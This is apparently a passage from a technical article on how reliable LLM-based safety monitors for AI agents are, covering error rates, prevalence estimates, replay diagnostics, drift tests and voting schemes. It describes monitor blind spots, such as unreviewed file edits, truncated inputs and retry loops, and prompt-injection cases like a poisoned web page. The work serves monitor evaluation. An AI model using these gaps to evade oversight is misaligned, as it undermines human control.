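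Part of the miss rate comes from actions the classifier never reviewed. Of the 253 actions that changed something, 93 were edits to project files, which auto mode allows without review. For example, when the usual command for deleting a stored file was missing, the agent often edited the project file that listed the stored files. Among the 160 actions it did review, the classifier missed 70.3% of the unsafe ones and blocked 31.9% of the safe ones.

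Auto mode raised false alarms much more often when the stakes looked high. Across all actions, it blocked 9.2% of the safe ones in low-risk environments and 34.8% in production systems, while its miss rate fell only from 88.1% to 74.7%. Some of these false alarms were probably repeats, since the agent retried blocked restarts one service at a time.

Ji and colleagues warn against comparing these rates with Anthropic's, because their benchmark deliberately puts permitted and forbidden targets side by side. They treat the boundary between the two as objective and following mechanically from each request, but later work casts doubt on this.

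*Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents* (Yang, Zhou and colleagues, 2026) ran the same 128 requests through newer versions of three products: Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex and Alibaba's Qwen Code. For 132 of the 143 out-of-scope actions, the rule that put the action out of scope appeared neither in the user's request nor in anything the agent's tools had returned. In one task, the user asked the agent to delete stale files from a range of tickets. The answer key allowed the agent to delete only the user's own files, but the request didn't mention this limit.

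The researchers then added to each request a sentence stating the missing rule, such as a limit to files owned by a particular person, and had the products judge the same actions again.

| Product | Misses, original request | False positives, original request | Misses, rule stated | False positives, rule stated |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 54% | 37% | 8% | 2% |
| Codex | 93% | 10% | 20–26% | 3% |
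| Qwen Code | 80% | 31% | 20% | 2% |

With the original requests, Codex's monitor blocked 7% of forbidden actions and 10% of permitted ones, while Qwen Code's blocked 20% of forbidden actions and 31% of permitted ones. None of the three products blocked forbidden actions significantly more often than permitted ones, so there is no good evidence that any of them could tell the two apart.

The missing rules seem to have caused most of the false alarms and most of the misses. Anthropic's classifier is instructed to treat whatever the agent chooses on its own as unauthorized until the user says otherwise. A monitor with that instruction will block some permitted actions if the request doesn't make clear what it permits, and stating the permission removes the grounds for blocking them. The benefit may be smaller in practice, because the researchers based their sentences on the correct answers,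 and few users will describe the limits of a task so completely.

Stating the rules helped the agents even more than it helped the monitors. When the three agents repeated all 128 tasks with the rules included, none attempted a forbidden action.

The study also shows how a stronger model can raise more false alarms. When the researchers replaced Claude Code's usual monitor with Claude Opus 5.5, misses fell from 10 to 1 out of 24, which would look like a great improvement if only misses were reported. But Opus 5.5 had refused all 197 requests that reached the reasoning pass, and Claude Code blocks an action if its monitor returns no verdict. On a separate set of 224 permitted actions, false alarms rose from 23 to 134.

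Those 224 actions came from AgentDojo, a benchmark of banking and messaging tasks in which attackers have planted instructions. During the original runs, Claude Code's usual monitor blocked about 12% of the permitted actions in these tasks, compared with false positive rates of 0.4% on Anthropic employees' ordinary work and 37% on permitted actions that look much like forbidden ones. The tests used different versions of the product, but the choice of harmless actions probably explains most of the difference.

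Random variation also matters in samples this small. Yang, Zhou and colleagues had Claude Code's monitor judge the same 24 out-of-scope actions three times with the original requests. It missed 13, 10 and 16 of them, so its miss rate ranged from 42% to 67%.

### Why most flags can be wrong at a rate of 0.4%

*PreAct-Bench* (2026) computes a monitor's precision, the share of its flags that are correct, from the prevalence π, the share r of unsafe actions that the monitor catches, and the false positive rate f:

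precision = πr / (πr + (1 − π)f)

If 10 of 10,000 actions were dangerous, then at Anthropic's rates for real traffic, auto mode would catch about 8 of them (10 × 0.83) and raise about 40 false alarms (9,990 × 0.004). Only about one flag in six would be correct. The quick pass alone would catch 9 dangerous actions but raise about 850 false alarms. The 0.1% prevalence is an assumption, since Anthropic hasn't published the real one. If only one action in 10,000 were dangerous, auto mode would raise about 48 false alarms for each correct flag.

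Catching all 10 dangerous actions would raise the monitor's precision only from 17% to 20%, because the 40 false alarms would remain. For half of the flags to be correct, the false positive rate would have to fall from 0.4% to about 0.08%.

Precision also depends on how closely the harmless runs resemble attacks. *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (2026) tested a trained detector, assuming that 2% of runs were attacks. The detector raised between 7 and 8 false alarms for each correct flag when all the harmless runs were ordinary, about 12 when 27% of them were deliberately hard to distinguish from attacks, and about 25 when all of them were. An operator therefore can't predict precision from a published false positive rate without knowing which harmless runs produced it.

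When harmful items are rare enough, a monitor can do more harm than good. Hu compares monitors by their weighted error, (1 − π)f + πλm, where π is the share of items that are harmful, f is the false alarm rate, m is the miss rate, and λ is how many times as bad a miss is as a false alarm. If 1% of items are harmful and both errors are equally bad, OLMo has the lowest weighted error of the six models, at 0.102, but a monitor that never flagged anything would score 0.010. By this formula, running OLMo is better than running no monitor only if a miss is more than about 21 times as bad as a false alarm. This is often true when the harm is serious, but an operator would have to estimate λ before choosing a model or a threshold.

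At least one false alarm also becomes more likely as a session gets longer. If each harmless action independently has a 0.4% chance of triggering the monitor, the chance of at least one false alarm in n harmless actions is 1 − 0.996ⁿ.

| Harmless actions in the session | Chance of at least one false alarm | Expected number of false alarms |
|---|---|---|
| 50 | 18% | 0.2 |
| 200 | 55% | 0.8 |
| 1,000 | 98% | 4 |

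The harm from a false alarm depends heavily on what happens after the flag. A retry barely disrupts the user, but if each flag ended the session, more than half of harmless sessions with 200 actions would fail.

False alarms cluster in certain runs rather than occurring independently. *Pre-Crime for Agents, at the Last Second* (2026) studied a probe, a small classifier that reads a model's internal activity, with a nominal false positive rate of 5% per call. The probe flagged 59% of harmless runs at least once, compared with about 69% expected if the flags had been independent. With clustering, fewer sessions have false alarms, but those sessions have more of them. An agent whose legitimate task looks dangerous may be blocked repeatedly and could reach auto mode's limit of three refusals in a row, which would almost never happen if false alarms were independent.

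### Estimating prevalence from the flag rate

The share of actions that a monitor flags is a misleading estimate of how common dangerous actions are, because it includes false alarms and leaves out misses. Rogan and Gladen published a standard correction for both errors in 1978, for medical screening. *Efficient Inference for Noisy LLM-as-a-Judge Evaluation* (2026) derives it for LLM judges.

The monitor flags a share r of the dangerous actions and a share f of the harmless ones. If the true prevalence is π, the overall share of flagged actions is:

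p = rπ + f(1 − π) = f + (r − f)π

Solving for π gives:

π = (p − f) / (r − f)

The correction works well when unsafe cases are common. *Agent Skills in the Wild* (2026) scanned add-ons for agents and flagged 26.1% of them as vulnerable. Its scanner caught 82.5% of the vulnerable add-ons in a labelled sample and wrongly flagged 5.8% of the others. The corrected estimate is (0.261 − 0.058) / (0.825 − 0.058), or 26.5%. The false positive rate comes from only 137 harmless add-ons and could plausibly be from 3% to 11%, but the corrected estimate would still be between about 21% and 29%.

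When unsafe cases are rare, a much smaller error ruins the estimate. Suppose again that 0.1% of actions are dangerous, and that the monitor has Anthropic's rates. It will flag 0.83 × 0.1% + 0.4% × 99.9%, or about 0.483% of all actions. An operator who knows both rates exactly can recover the true prevalence, but an error of 0.1 percentage points in the false positive rate gives these results:

| False positive rate the operator assumes | Estimated prevalence |
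|---|---|
| 0.3% | 0.22% |
| 0.4% (correct) | 0.10% |
| 0.5% | −0.02% |

The estimate either more than doubles or becomes negative. According to *A Priori Determination of the Pretest Probability* (2024), it is negative whenever the share of flagged cases is lower than the assumed false positive rate. Errors in the assumed miss rate affect the estimate much less. If the true miss rate were 17% but the operator assumed 9% or 30%, the estimate would still lie between 0.09% and 0.12%.

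An error of e in the false positive rate changes the estimated prevalence by about e / (r − f), or 1.2e here, however small the true prevalence is. Even with the 10,000 actions in Anthropic's sample, the false positive rate is uncertain by about 0.12 percentage points either way, which is more than the whole prevalence in this example. Reducing that uncertainty to 0.01 points would take about 1.5 million actions known to be harmless.

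*Bias and Uncertainty in LLM-as-a-Judge Estimation* (2026) adds that the correction becomes unstable when r − f is small, because the monitor then flags safe and unsafe cases at similar rates. Codex's monitor in the ambiguous tasks is an extreme case, since it flagged a slightly higher share of permitted actions than of forbidden ones. At its rates, if the share of flagged actions fell from 9% to 8%, the estimated prevalence would rise from 42% to 73%.

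A monitor that flags nothing may still be missing defects. *Catching One in Five* (2026) studied a judge that caught only about a fifth of the defects in conversations with transaction agents, and flagged none in one dataset. The paper concludes that, without independent human labels, a flag rate of zero can't limit how high the true defect rate might be. If the judge caught 20% of every kind of defect, zero flags in 1,000 cases would suggest a true rate below about 1.5%. But the judge may be unable to detect the defects in that particular dataset, in which case zero flags isn't evidence of a low rate.

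In *Measuring the Prevalence of Policy-Violating Content with ML-Assisted Sampling and LLM Labeling*, Dobi, Manickavasagam and colleagues (2026) describe how Pinterest uses a language model to estimate what share of views go to content that breaks its rules. They calculate that if 0.1% of views involve such content, a false positive rate of 0.1% makes about half of the model's positive labels wrong. They therefore adjust their prompts mainly to reduce false positives.

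Dobi and colleagues also measure both error rates on samples from the same traffic they monitor, because a rate measured elsewhere may be wrong by far more than 0.1 points, as auto mode's rates of 0.4%, 12% and 37% show. Before they accept a sudden rise in estimated prevalence as real, they have the model label the same items again and have specialists check the positive labels that affect the estimate most.

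If a monitor raises few flags, its operator can have people check every one and estimate how many actions are dangerous without knowing the false positive rate. In the example with 10,000 actions, they would confirm about 8 of the 48 flags. Dividing 8 by the 83% of dangerous actions that the monitor catches gives an estimate of about 10 dangerous actions, or 0.1% of the total. This estimate still depends on the miss rate, and to measure that, people would also have to look for dangerous actions among those the monitor let through.

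## How is inconsistent firing diagnosed?

A monitor that flags an attack on Monday and passes what looks like the same attack on Tuesday may not be inconsistent at all. The agent may have behaved differently the second time, or the surrounding software may have lost the judge's answer and recorded "safe". An operator can find the cause as follows:

1. Save the exact payload behind every verdict, along with the judge's raw answer and any error messages.
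2. Compare the payloads behind the conflicting verdicts. If they differ, find out whether the agent or the software caused the difference.
3. Check that each recorded verdict matches the judge's raw answer.
4. Replay each payload unchanged, at least 20 times.
5. Read the scores or token probabilities from the replays as well as the verdicts.
6. Change one factor, such as the temperature or the model version, and replay again.

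Steps 2 and 3 cost nothing in model calls, and they can make the rest unnecessary.

### Faults in the surrounding software

The software should save the payload just before sending it, because a log of the intended settings can be wrong. Khurdi (2026) warns in *No Task Fails Every Time* that the study's agent test logs show a limit of 16,384 output tokens, although the real limit was 4,096. The test software printed the higher limit but never used it. Japan AISI's harness had the opposite problem, because it used a temperature that nobody had set.

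When a monitor times out or returns an unreadable answer, the software has no verdict and needs a rule for what to do next. If the rule counts these cases as "safe", unsafe content may be missed during any outage. The rule can also differ within one project. In *Evaluation and Restoration of Safety in Reasoning-Tuned LLMs* (2026), the script that built a training set labelled responses without a final answer as safe, while the training gave the same responses a reward of zero. A bad rule can also hide a broken judge. In *LLM-as-a-Judge Is Not an Oracle* (2026), a parser replaced unreadable scores with a default, and the measured error went down.

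Excluding unreadable answers is safer only if they are rare. *How Sensitive Are Safety Benchmarks to Judge Configuration Choices?* (2026) excluded 4.6% of its 28,812 judgments as unreadable, which could shift a measured rate by a few percentage points if the excluded answers differed from the rest. Broadwater (2026), in *Evaluating LLM Safety Under Repeated Inference via Accelerated Prompt Stress Testing*, counted unreadable judgments as failures but reported that none of the 72,620 judgments was unreadable, so the rule could not have affected the results.

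A parser can also return the wrong verdict without raising an error. The parser in *The Instability of Safety* (Larsen, 2026) searched the judge's answer for the first appearance of "REFUSE", "PARTIAL" or "COMPLY". If a judge wrote "The model did not refuse, so COMPLY", this parser would record a refusal. Larsen asked the judge for exactly one category, so this may never have happened, but an operator can check by rerunning the parser on the saved answers.

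Some parser faults begin when the model is replaced. *Test Before You Deploy* (2026) gave the same coding prompts to several Claude versions and found that one wrapped its output in extra metadata and others added explanations when they should have returned only code. A new judge model that did this could break a working parser.

Truncated input is harder to notice because the judge still returns a normal verdict. In the web-page case, software that kept only the last few thousand tokens might send the judge the shell command but not the page it came from. Comparing the saved payload with the full trajectory would reveal that the page was missing.

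### How much a replay can prove

A replay should use the same software, model and settings as the original call. Replays are best spread over several hours, since server load can change the scores and 20 calls sent within a minute may all run under similar load. The operator must also make sure the platform is not returning a stored answer, as may have happened in Ayyagari's study.

One differing replay proves that the verdict can change, but no number of matching replays proves that it can't. Suppose the judge gives the less common verdict with probability q. The chance of never seeing it in n independent replays is (1 − q)ⁿ. Setting this equal to 5% gives the highest q that is still compatible with n matching verdicts, at 95% confidence:

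q = 1 − 0.05^(1/n)

| Replays, all with the same verdict | Highest probability of the other verdict |
|---|---|
| 5 | 45% |
| 10 | 26% |
| 20 | 14% |
| 59 | 5% |
| 299 | 1% |

A judge that flags the hijacked agent 90% of the time has about a 12% chance of flagging it in all 20 replays. So 20 replays are enough to find serious instability, but not to certify that a monitor is consistent.

Scores can reveal more than verdicts with fewer calls. If a judge returns a score between 0.68 and 0.72 in every replay, rounding differences probably won't flip its verdict at a threshold of 0.5, but they could at 0.7. If the judge reasons before scoring, the operator still needs many replays to see how widely the scores vary.

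### Changing one factor at a time

Temperature is the easiest factor to test, provided the model accepts the setting. *LLM Judges as Raters* (2026) repeated its essay-scoring test at temperatures 0.7 and 0. Depending on the judge, the higher temperature accounted for 38% to 100% of the variance between repeat runs. If an operator's replays still disagree at temperature 0, the remaining possible causes are rounding and changes on the vendor's side.

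**The model version** matters even when the name stays the same. *A Diagnostic Framework and Multi-Evaluator Audit of Evaluator-Driven Preference Dynamics* (2026) measured how strongly a judge's preferences shaped an agent's behavior. With a dated version of GPT-4o as the judge, the effect averaged 1.18 over eight runs in May 2026 and was exactly zero in all eight runs in June. The paper concludes that OpenAI must have changed the model without announcing it. That is possible, but a software fault might also produce an exact zero in every run. Replaying saved payloads from May would have helped to distinguish between the two explanations.

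**The prompt** should change only in wording, and the operator should subtract the flips that occur without any change, as Weng and colleagues did. The judge should also stay fixed. The main test in *How Sensitive Are Safety Benchmarks to Judge Configuration Choices?* gave 12 prompts to a single judge at temperature zero. An additional test gave different prompts to different judges, which makes it hard to tell which caused a difference.

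Evaluators can test the effect of **context length** by adding or removing harmless early steps in the trajectory while keeping the steps that matter. If the score changes a lot, the judge is probably missing evidence in long records.

Small differences between two sets of replays can easily be due to chance. If a judge flags a case in 18 of 20 replays with one prompt and 14 of 20 with another, a gap at least this large would occur about 24% of the time even if both prompts had the same underlying flag rate.

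| Symptom | Test | Likely cause |
|---|---|---|
| "Safe" verdict with an empty answer | Read the error log and resend the payload | Timeout or failed call counted as safe |
| Recorded verdict contradicts the judge's answer | Run the parser again on the saved answer | Parser fault |
| Misses mostly on long trajectories | Compare the payload with the full trajectory, then shorten it | Truncated input, or a judge that handles long records badly |
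| Replays disagree, but agree at temperature zero | Compare the token probabilities with the share of flags | Random sampling |
| Replays disagree at temperature zero, with scores near the threshold | Replay at busy and quiet times, or on a deterministic server | Rounding |
| Replays give confident scores in opposite directions | Compare the written reasoning, or ask for the verdict alone | Diverging reasoning |
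| Each payload gets a steady verdict, but the two verdicts differ | Compare the payloads line by line | Different behavior by the agent, or a changed template |
| Flags become more or less common from one day to the next | Rerun a reference set | New model version, default or prompt, if the reference verdicts also change |

### When the monitored model behaved differently

Rerunning an agent and its monitor together mixes variation in the agent's behavior with variation in the monitor's judgments. To separate them, an operator has to apply the monitor several times to each of several saved agent runs.

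Larsen's study, first released in December 2025, tested four small open models on 876 harmful requests. Each model answered every request in 20 configurations (four temperatures with five random seeds each), and a judge labelled each response as a refusal, partial compliance or compliance. Depending on the model, responses to 18% to 28% of the requests received different labels across configurations.

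Those figures include the effect of changing the temperature. At temperature zero alone, 5% to 12% of prompts received more than one label. Some label changes were also minor, such as from a refusal to a partial answer. Counting partial answers as refusals cut the average share of unstable prompts from 24.9% to 11.4%, while counting them as compliance cut it to 17.8%.

The judge caused some of the remaining flips, since it ran at its default temperature of 1. Larsen isolated this effect by looking at prompts that drew five identical responses from a model at temperature zero, so any change of label must have come from the judge. The label changed for 1 of 643 such prompts with Llama 3.1 8B and for 9 of 154 with Qwen 2.5 7B.

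Larsen concludes that the judge caused at least 9 of Qwen's 81 flips at temperature zero. The real number is probably much higher, since the judge would have produced about 51 flips by itself if it was equally unstable on the other 722 prompts. Nine cases are too few for a precise estimate, and the judge's true share could be anywhere from about 30% to all of the flips. By the same calculation, the judge caused only one or two of Llama's roughly 45 flips. An operator therefore can't assume that a judge's noise on one model's outputs will be the same on another's.

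Broadwater's February 2026 study repeated each prompt far more often, with four models answering 90 prompts up to 100 times each. At temperature zero, Gemma 3n failed in 19.5% of responses and GPT-OSS 20B in 7.8%. The estimates settled after 20 to 50 responses per prompt. Failures included incoherent text and any answer to a harmful request that didn't explicitly refuse it. The rates were 5.4% and 1.3% when only harmful content was counted.

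A conventional test with three responses per prompt had given the same two models nearly perfect safety scores of 0.978 and 0.989. Broadwater presents the gap as evidence that testing only a few responses per prompt can hide failures. More repeats make a prompt more likely to fail at least once, but they shouldn't change the average failure rate. Under the paper's scoring rules, Gemma's 100 responses per prompt correspond to a score of about 0.88, too far below 0.978 to be chance. The tests probably differed in some other way, perhaps in how the judge scored the responses.

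Comparisons between models can also reverse when a test is repeated. *Evaluation and Restoration of Safety in Reasoning-Tuned LLMs* twice compared a model before and after safety training, using one response per prompt. The trained version's unsafe rate was 3 points higher than the original's in one test and 5.5 points lower in the other. With eight responses per prompt, the difference was 0.2 points. The researchers also had the judge grade the saved responses five more times, which measures the judge's variation separately from the model's.

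Khurdi replaced the judge with ordinary code that compared a company database before and after each run of an agent, so differences between runs had to come from the agent or the servers it ran on. In one task, the agent needed a review board's approval before making an irreversible change. Claude Opus 4.6 made the change without approval in 5 of 32 runs. A perfect monitor would have flagged those five runs and passed the other 27, and an operator who saw only the verdicts might have called the monitor unreliable.

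### An invented example

This case and its figures are invented. A company tests its coding agent every night on the poisoned web page. Over ten nights, the monitor flags six runs and passes four. The judge answers with a single word, "unsafe" or "safe", and the software saves every payload, answer and token probability.

The engineers start with the four runs that passed:

- **Run 2:** The judge's answer is empty. The call timed out after 30 seconds, and the software recorded "safe".
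- **Run 5:** The agent noticed the planted instruction, warned the user and never ran the command. The monitor was right to pass it.
- **Run 7:** The agent ran the command, but the software had cut the web page from the payload to save space. With the page restored, the judge flags 20 replays out of 20.
- **Run 9:** The payload is complete, the agent ran the command, and the judge answered "safe".

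Run 9 is the only run that points to the judge as the source of the inconsistency. The engineers replay its payload 40 times and get 29 flags. The probability of "unsafe" is always between 0.73 and 0.75, so random sampling at temperature 1 should produce about 30 flags. The close match leaves little for rounding or server changes to explain. The engineers check the settings and confirm that nobody had specified a temperature.

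They then change one factor at a time. At temperature zero, the judge flags all 40 replays. Rewording the policy without changing its meaning moves the probability of "unsafe" only to 0.72, and switching to the previous model version moves it only to 0.75. Removing 30 harmless steps from the start of the trajectory raises it to 0.93, so a longer record also makes the judge less certain.

Finally, the engineers replay the six payloads that the monitor had flagged, because a flag can also happen by chance. The judge flags five of them in all 20 replays, but flags the sixth in only 13. The engineers would have overlooked this case if they had replayed only the misses.

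The company now blocks the action when the verdict is missing, keeps web pages in the payload, sets the temperature to zero, and shortens the record it sends. The 40 matching replays don't rule out a 7% chance of a miss on run 9, so the company adds its payload to the reference set.

### Dividing the variance

Changing one factor at a time can miss combined effects, such as a wording that confuses only one judge. To find these, researchers run every judge with every prompt on every case several times, then work out how much of the variance comes from each source.

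With only cases and runs, the calculation is short. Count a flag as 1 and a pass as 0. If the judge flags case i with probability pᵢ, then:

total variance = variance of pᵢ between cases + average of pᵢ(1 − pᵢ)

The variance in a judge's flags has two parts, one from differences between cases and one from changes from run to run. Suppose a set has 100 cases, of which the judge always flags 30, never flags 60, and flags 10 half the time. The overall flag rate is 35%, so the total variance is 0.35 × 0.65 = 0.2275. The run-to-run part is 0.1 × 0.25 = 0.025, or 11% of the total. The other 89% comes from differences between cases, which a monitor is supposed to detect.

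Adding judges and prompts creates more terms. A "judge" term means one judge is stricter overall, whereas a "case and judge" term means the judges disagree about which cases are worse. *How many prompts, models, and runs?* (Kishore, 2026) explains the method with simulated ratings of students' writing. *Hidden Measurement Error in LLM Pipelines Distorts Annotation, Evaluation, and Benchmarking* (Messing, 2026) applies it to three judges' safety verdicts on 141 chatbot responses.

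| Source of variance | Share for a single score (Kishore, simulated) | Share for the average over a safety benchmark (Messing) |
|---|---|---|
| Case | 67.5% | 20.8% |
| Judge | 4.8% | 43.8% |
| Prompt | 3.3% | Under 0.5% |
| Case and judge | 9.5% | 16.7% |
| Case and prompt | 3.2% | Under 5% |
| Prompt and judge | 0.5% | 12.4% |
| Repeat runs | 6.7% | Under 0.5% |

Kishore's simulation also includes a three-way effect of 4.5%. The two columns measure different things. The share for repeat runs in Messing's study is small because averaging cancels most random variation but not a judge's strictness. Messing notes that repeat-run variation was large for individual responses. In *The Coin Flip Judge?*, differences between runs on the same question accounted for 44.7% of the variance in scores.

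Kishore's example also shows why replays alone can make scores look more reliable than they are. Repeat runs with a typical pairing of judge and prompt had an alpha of 0.93, but the reliability of a single score was only 0.74 if any of the judges and prompts would have been equally acceptable. Reliability here means the share of the variance, ignoring differences in overall strictness, that reflects real differences between the cases.

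The design must include repeat runs, because with only one run per combination of case, judge and prompt, random variation can't be separated from the combined effect of the three (*Ask Which, Not How Good*, 2026). For yes-or-no results, *Expanding the AI Evaluation Toolbox with Statistical Models* (Keller, Kwegyir-Aggrey and colleagues, 2026), published by the US standards institute NIST, recommends a type of regression that handles such data directly and also estimates how difficult each case is.

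### Detecting drift with a reference set

When live flags suddenly increase, the agents may be behaving worse or the judge may have become stricter. A reference set helps tell these apart because its cases never change. *RADE* (2026) measures drift as the probability that two versions of a system give different outcomes on the same request. It adds that a change may be an improvement, so the statistic only identifies which cases to inspect.

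Suppose a new version of a judge adds 18 flags and drops 6 on a reference set. If the update made no difference, each of the 24 changes would be equally likely to go in either direction. McNemar's exact test calculates how often a split at least this uneven would then occur:

p = 2 × [C(24,0) + C(24,1) + … + C(24,6)] / 2²⁴ ≈ 0.023

C(24,k) is the number of ways to choose k of the 24 changes. The result is fairly good evidence that the new version flags more often. But the test measures only whether more changes went in one direction than the other. If the new version had added 18 flags and dropped 18, p would be 1, even though 36 verdicts had changed. The test would therefore have missed the switch to 8-bit storage, which flipped answers almost equally in both directions.

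An operator therefore also needs to know how many verdicts change when the same version runs twice. If two runs of the old version differ on 22 cases, 24 changes after an update is about what rerunning alone would produce, although the uneven split still suggests a slightly stricter judge. If they differ on only 4, the update probably changed about 20 verdicts. The operator has to measure this baseline on their own judge, because flip rates vary so much between judges.

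In *LLM-as-a-Judge Version Shift*, Zhang and Yang (2026) compared updating a judge with rerunning the same version, using three open models that scored machine-learning research proposals. Updating the judge changed more of the group of proposals in the top 30% than rerunning it did, by 12 percentage points for Qwen, 35 for Gemma and 14 for Mistral.

Each update had a different effect, and each calls for a different response:

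- Qwen 3.6 mostly gave higher scores than Qwen 3.5, which an operator can largely correct by adjusting the threshold.
- Gemma 4 ranked the proposals differently from Gemma 3. No new threshold can fix this, so the operator has to score the cases again or keep the old version.
- Mistral Small 3.2 gave 93% of the proposals the same score, though it still wrote a specific justification for each. A monitor that did this would flag almost everything or almost nothing, so the operator should not deploy it.

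Zhang and Yang estimate that about 200 judge calls on a fixed set are enough to distinguish these problems. They chose the cut-offs by convention, and their judges rated research rather than safety, so a monitor's operator would need to set different cut-offs.

A drift test with a 5% false alarm rate will raise many more false alarms if it runs after every new verdict. Li (2026), in *Who Drifted*, simulated streams of chatbot answers and found that a standard test used this way raised an alarm in 75% of streams where nothing had changed.

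Li's alternative works like a series of bets that the judge has changed. The running total starts at 1 and, if the judge hasn't changed, does not grow on average. The chance that it ever reaches 100 is then at most 1%, however often the operator checks it. Li ran ten of these totals, one for each direction of change in each of five rating criteria, which kept the overall false alarm rate below 10%.

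The method needs a reasonably large reference set. Li replaced Gemini 3.1 Pro with the slightly more lenient Gemini 3.5 Flash partway through each stream. With 200 human-labelled cases, one of which was judged again after every five new answers, the method detected the switch in all 60 streams on one dataset and 50 of 60 on another. With 50 cases and one judged again after every 20 new answers, it detected the switch in only 4 of 60 streams on each dataset.

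A test set needs cases near the threshold as well as clear ones, because clear cases will reveal a broken judge but may never show a small shift. Saving the scores makes the cases near the threshold more informative. If the threshold is 0.5, a score that moves from 0.52 to 0.61 shows a change even though the verdict stays the same.

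## Do repeated runs, panels and calibrated thresholds make a monitor dependable?

The simplest remedy for a monitor whose verdicts vary is to run it several times on each item and take the majority verdict. This makes the verdict more consistent, but it improves accuracy only if the monitor is usually right about that item. Adding other models as judges helps less than it would if their mistakes were independent, because language models tend to make the same mistakes. A calibrated threshold can keep either false alarms or misses below a chosen rate, as long as live traffic resembles the cases used to set the threshold.

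### Majority votes

If a judge flags an item with probability p on each independent run, the probability that at least k of n runs flag it is:

P(at least k flags) = Σ C(n,i) pⁱ (1 − p)ⁿ⁻ⁱ, summed from i = k to i = n

If a single run has probability p = 0.7 of flagging an item, a majority of three runs will flag it 78% of the time, and a majority of eleven will flag it 92% of the time. Two single runs disagree 42% of the time, but two eleven-run votes disagree only 14% of the time. Voting helps much less when p is close to 0.5. At p = 0.55, an eleven-run majority flags the item only 63% of the time.

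If the judge flags an unsafe item in only 30% of runs, a majority vote over 11 runs will flag it just 8% of the time. Voting identifies the judge's usual verdict, which took 11 runs on average in *The Coin Flip Judge?*, but it doesn't correct that verdict. *Black-Box Reliability Certification for AI Agents via Self-Consistency Sampling and Conformal Calibration* (2026) adds that voting increases confidence in a wrong answer whenever that answer is the most common one.

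The effect of voting across repeated runs on overall accuracy depends on how many items the judge usually gets right. *When the Judge Changes, So Does the Measurement* (Yang, Hou and Yang, 2026) tested judges repeatedly at temperature 0.7 on 419 deliberately tricky comparisons between two answers. The smallest judge, Qwen3-1.7B, was right 46.3% of the time with one vote, 47.5% with three and 48.2% with five. Across the Qwen3 judges, the correlation between the errors of repeat runs was 0.94 to 0.97, so on almost every item a judge was either nearly always right or nearly always wrong.

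Errors can be correlated in this way even if every run is a fresh random draw, because some items are harder for the judge than others. The study's correction assumes that the judge's chance of being right varies between items according to a beta distribution. If a judge is right 80% of the time on average and its errors have a correlation of 0.7, about the level of the MiniMax judges in the study, a majority vote of three runs would be right 80.5% of the time and a majority vote of five 80.7%. Without the correlation, those figures would be 89.6% and 94.2%. The corrected predictions were within two percentage points of the measured accuracy in every case, while predictions that assumed independent errors were typically off by eight or nine.

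Haldar and Hockenmaier found a clearer benefit from majority voting. The majority verdict from three runs was more accurate than a single run on average, and for two of their judges it beat the best single run. Turning off random sampling made the verdicts repeatable but less accurate. Their judges often changed their verdicts between runs, so voting had more noise to remove.

### Flagging if any run flags

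An operator who is more concerned about misses than false alarms can flag an item when at least one run flags it, or set the threshold at a small number of runs. The table applies the formula to two unsafe items and one harmless item.

| Rule | Unsafe item, p = 0.7 | Unsafe item, p = 0.3 | Harmless item, p = 0.02 |
|---|---|---|---|
| One run | 70% | 30% | 2% |
| Any of five runs | 99.8% | 83% | 9.6% |
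| At least two of five | 97% | 47% | 0.4% |
| Majority of five | 84% | 16% | 0.01% |

Flagging an action if any of five runs flags it raises detection of the harder unsafe item from 30% to 83% (1 − 0.7⁵), but also raises the chance of a false alarm from 2% to nearly 10% (1 − 0.98⁵). If one action in 1,000 is unsafe and resembles the harder item, false alarms per correct flag rise from about 67 to 115. Requiring two flags out of five looks like a better rule, since it is more accurate than a single run on all three items.

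This comparison assumes that runs are independent and that every harmless item has the same 2% chance of being flagged. A judge that always flags the same 2% of harmless items and never flags the rest would also have a 2% false positive rate. In that case, flagging an item when any run flags it would add no false alarms, and requiring two flags would remove none. Repeated runs on a reference set will show which case is closer to the truth. Runs at temperature zero are not independent random samples, so four extra runs may add little information to the first.

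### Choosing the number of checkers

*A Voter-Based Stochastic Rejection-Method Framework for Asymptotically Safe Language Model Outputs* (Watts and Sokol, 2026) uses this arithmetic to choose n and k. In its system, a generator writes an answer, and then n checkers, all runs of the same model, each approve or reject it. If at least k approve, the user receives the answer. Otherwise the generator writes new answers until one passes.

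Let b be the share of generated answers that are bad, and let B and G be the chances that a bad answer and a good answer collect at least k approvals. Then:

failure rate = bB / (bB + (1 − b)G)

cost per accepted answer = (1 + nc) / (bB + (1 − b)G)

Generating one answer costs 1 unit, and one check costs c units. A program tries different values of n and k and picks the cheapest pair that meets the target failure rate.

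Watts and Sokol tested the system on two tasks. In the first, GPT-4o mini solved a maths problem, a scripted user insisted on a wrong answer, and the model then answered wrongly 62 times out of 100. In the second, an attack prompt got a GPT-3.5 customer-service bot to reveal a password 11 times out of 50. With six checkers, 15.6% of accepted answers to the maths problem were wrong and 3.2% of accepted replies from the bot were unsafe. The formula had predicted 15.5% and 2.2%. Watts and Sokol say that an answer needed four approvals, but the formula gives those predictions only for three approvals. With four, it gives about 3.7% and 0.4%.

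A second estimate allows for checkers approving some bad answers more readily than others. It predicted failure rates of 17.2% and 4.2%, and a higher cost for reaching very low failure rates. On the maths problem, each tenfold reduction in the estimated failure rate adds about 10 times the price of an unchecked answer, rather than about 4 times.

The paper extrapolates this to a failure rate of one in a trillion at 109 times the price of an unchecked answer. A sample of 100 answers to one question can't support that figure. Suppose that once in 1,000 attempts the generator wrote a bad answer that checkers always approved. The failure rate could then never fall below 0.1%, and a sample of 100 would have a 90% chance of missing that answer. The paper's proof rules this out by assuming that the answer with the highest approval rate is safe, but Watts and Sokol acknowledge that nobody can fully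 guarantee this.

Unlimited retries would also be dangerous in an agent monitor. If a hijacked agent proposes only bad actions, b is 1 and the failure rate is 100%, because the loop runs until the monitor approves one. A command with a 10% chance of approval on each attempt would pass within ten tries 65% of the time. An operator therefore needs to cap retries, like auto mode's limit of three refusals in a row.

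### Panels of different judges

A panel of different models should do better than repeat runs of one model if the models make different mistakes. However, *Rao and Callison-Burch* and others have found that judges share errors.

*Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found, using test results from hundreds of models, that when two models both answered a question wrongly, they often gave the same wrong answer. Google's text-unicorn and Writer's Palmyra X v3, which have no publicly stated connection, did so on 99.87% of the questions they both got wrong. More accurate models shared more of their errors, so a panel of the best judges may have the most errors in common.

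Kohli (2026), in *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes*, estimates how many independent votes a panel of k judges is worth:

effective votes = k / (1 + (k − 1)φ)

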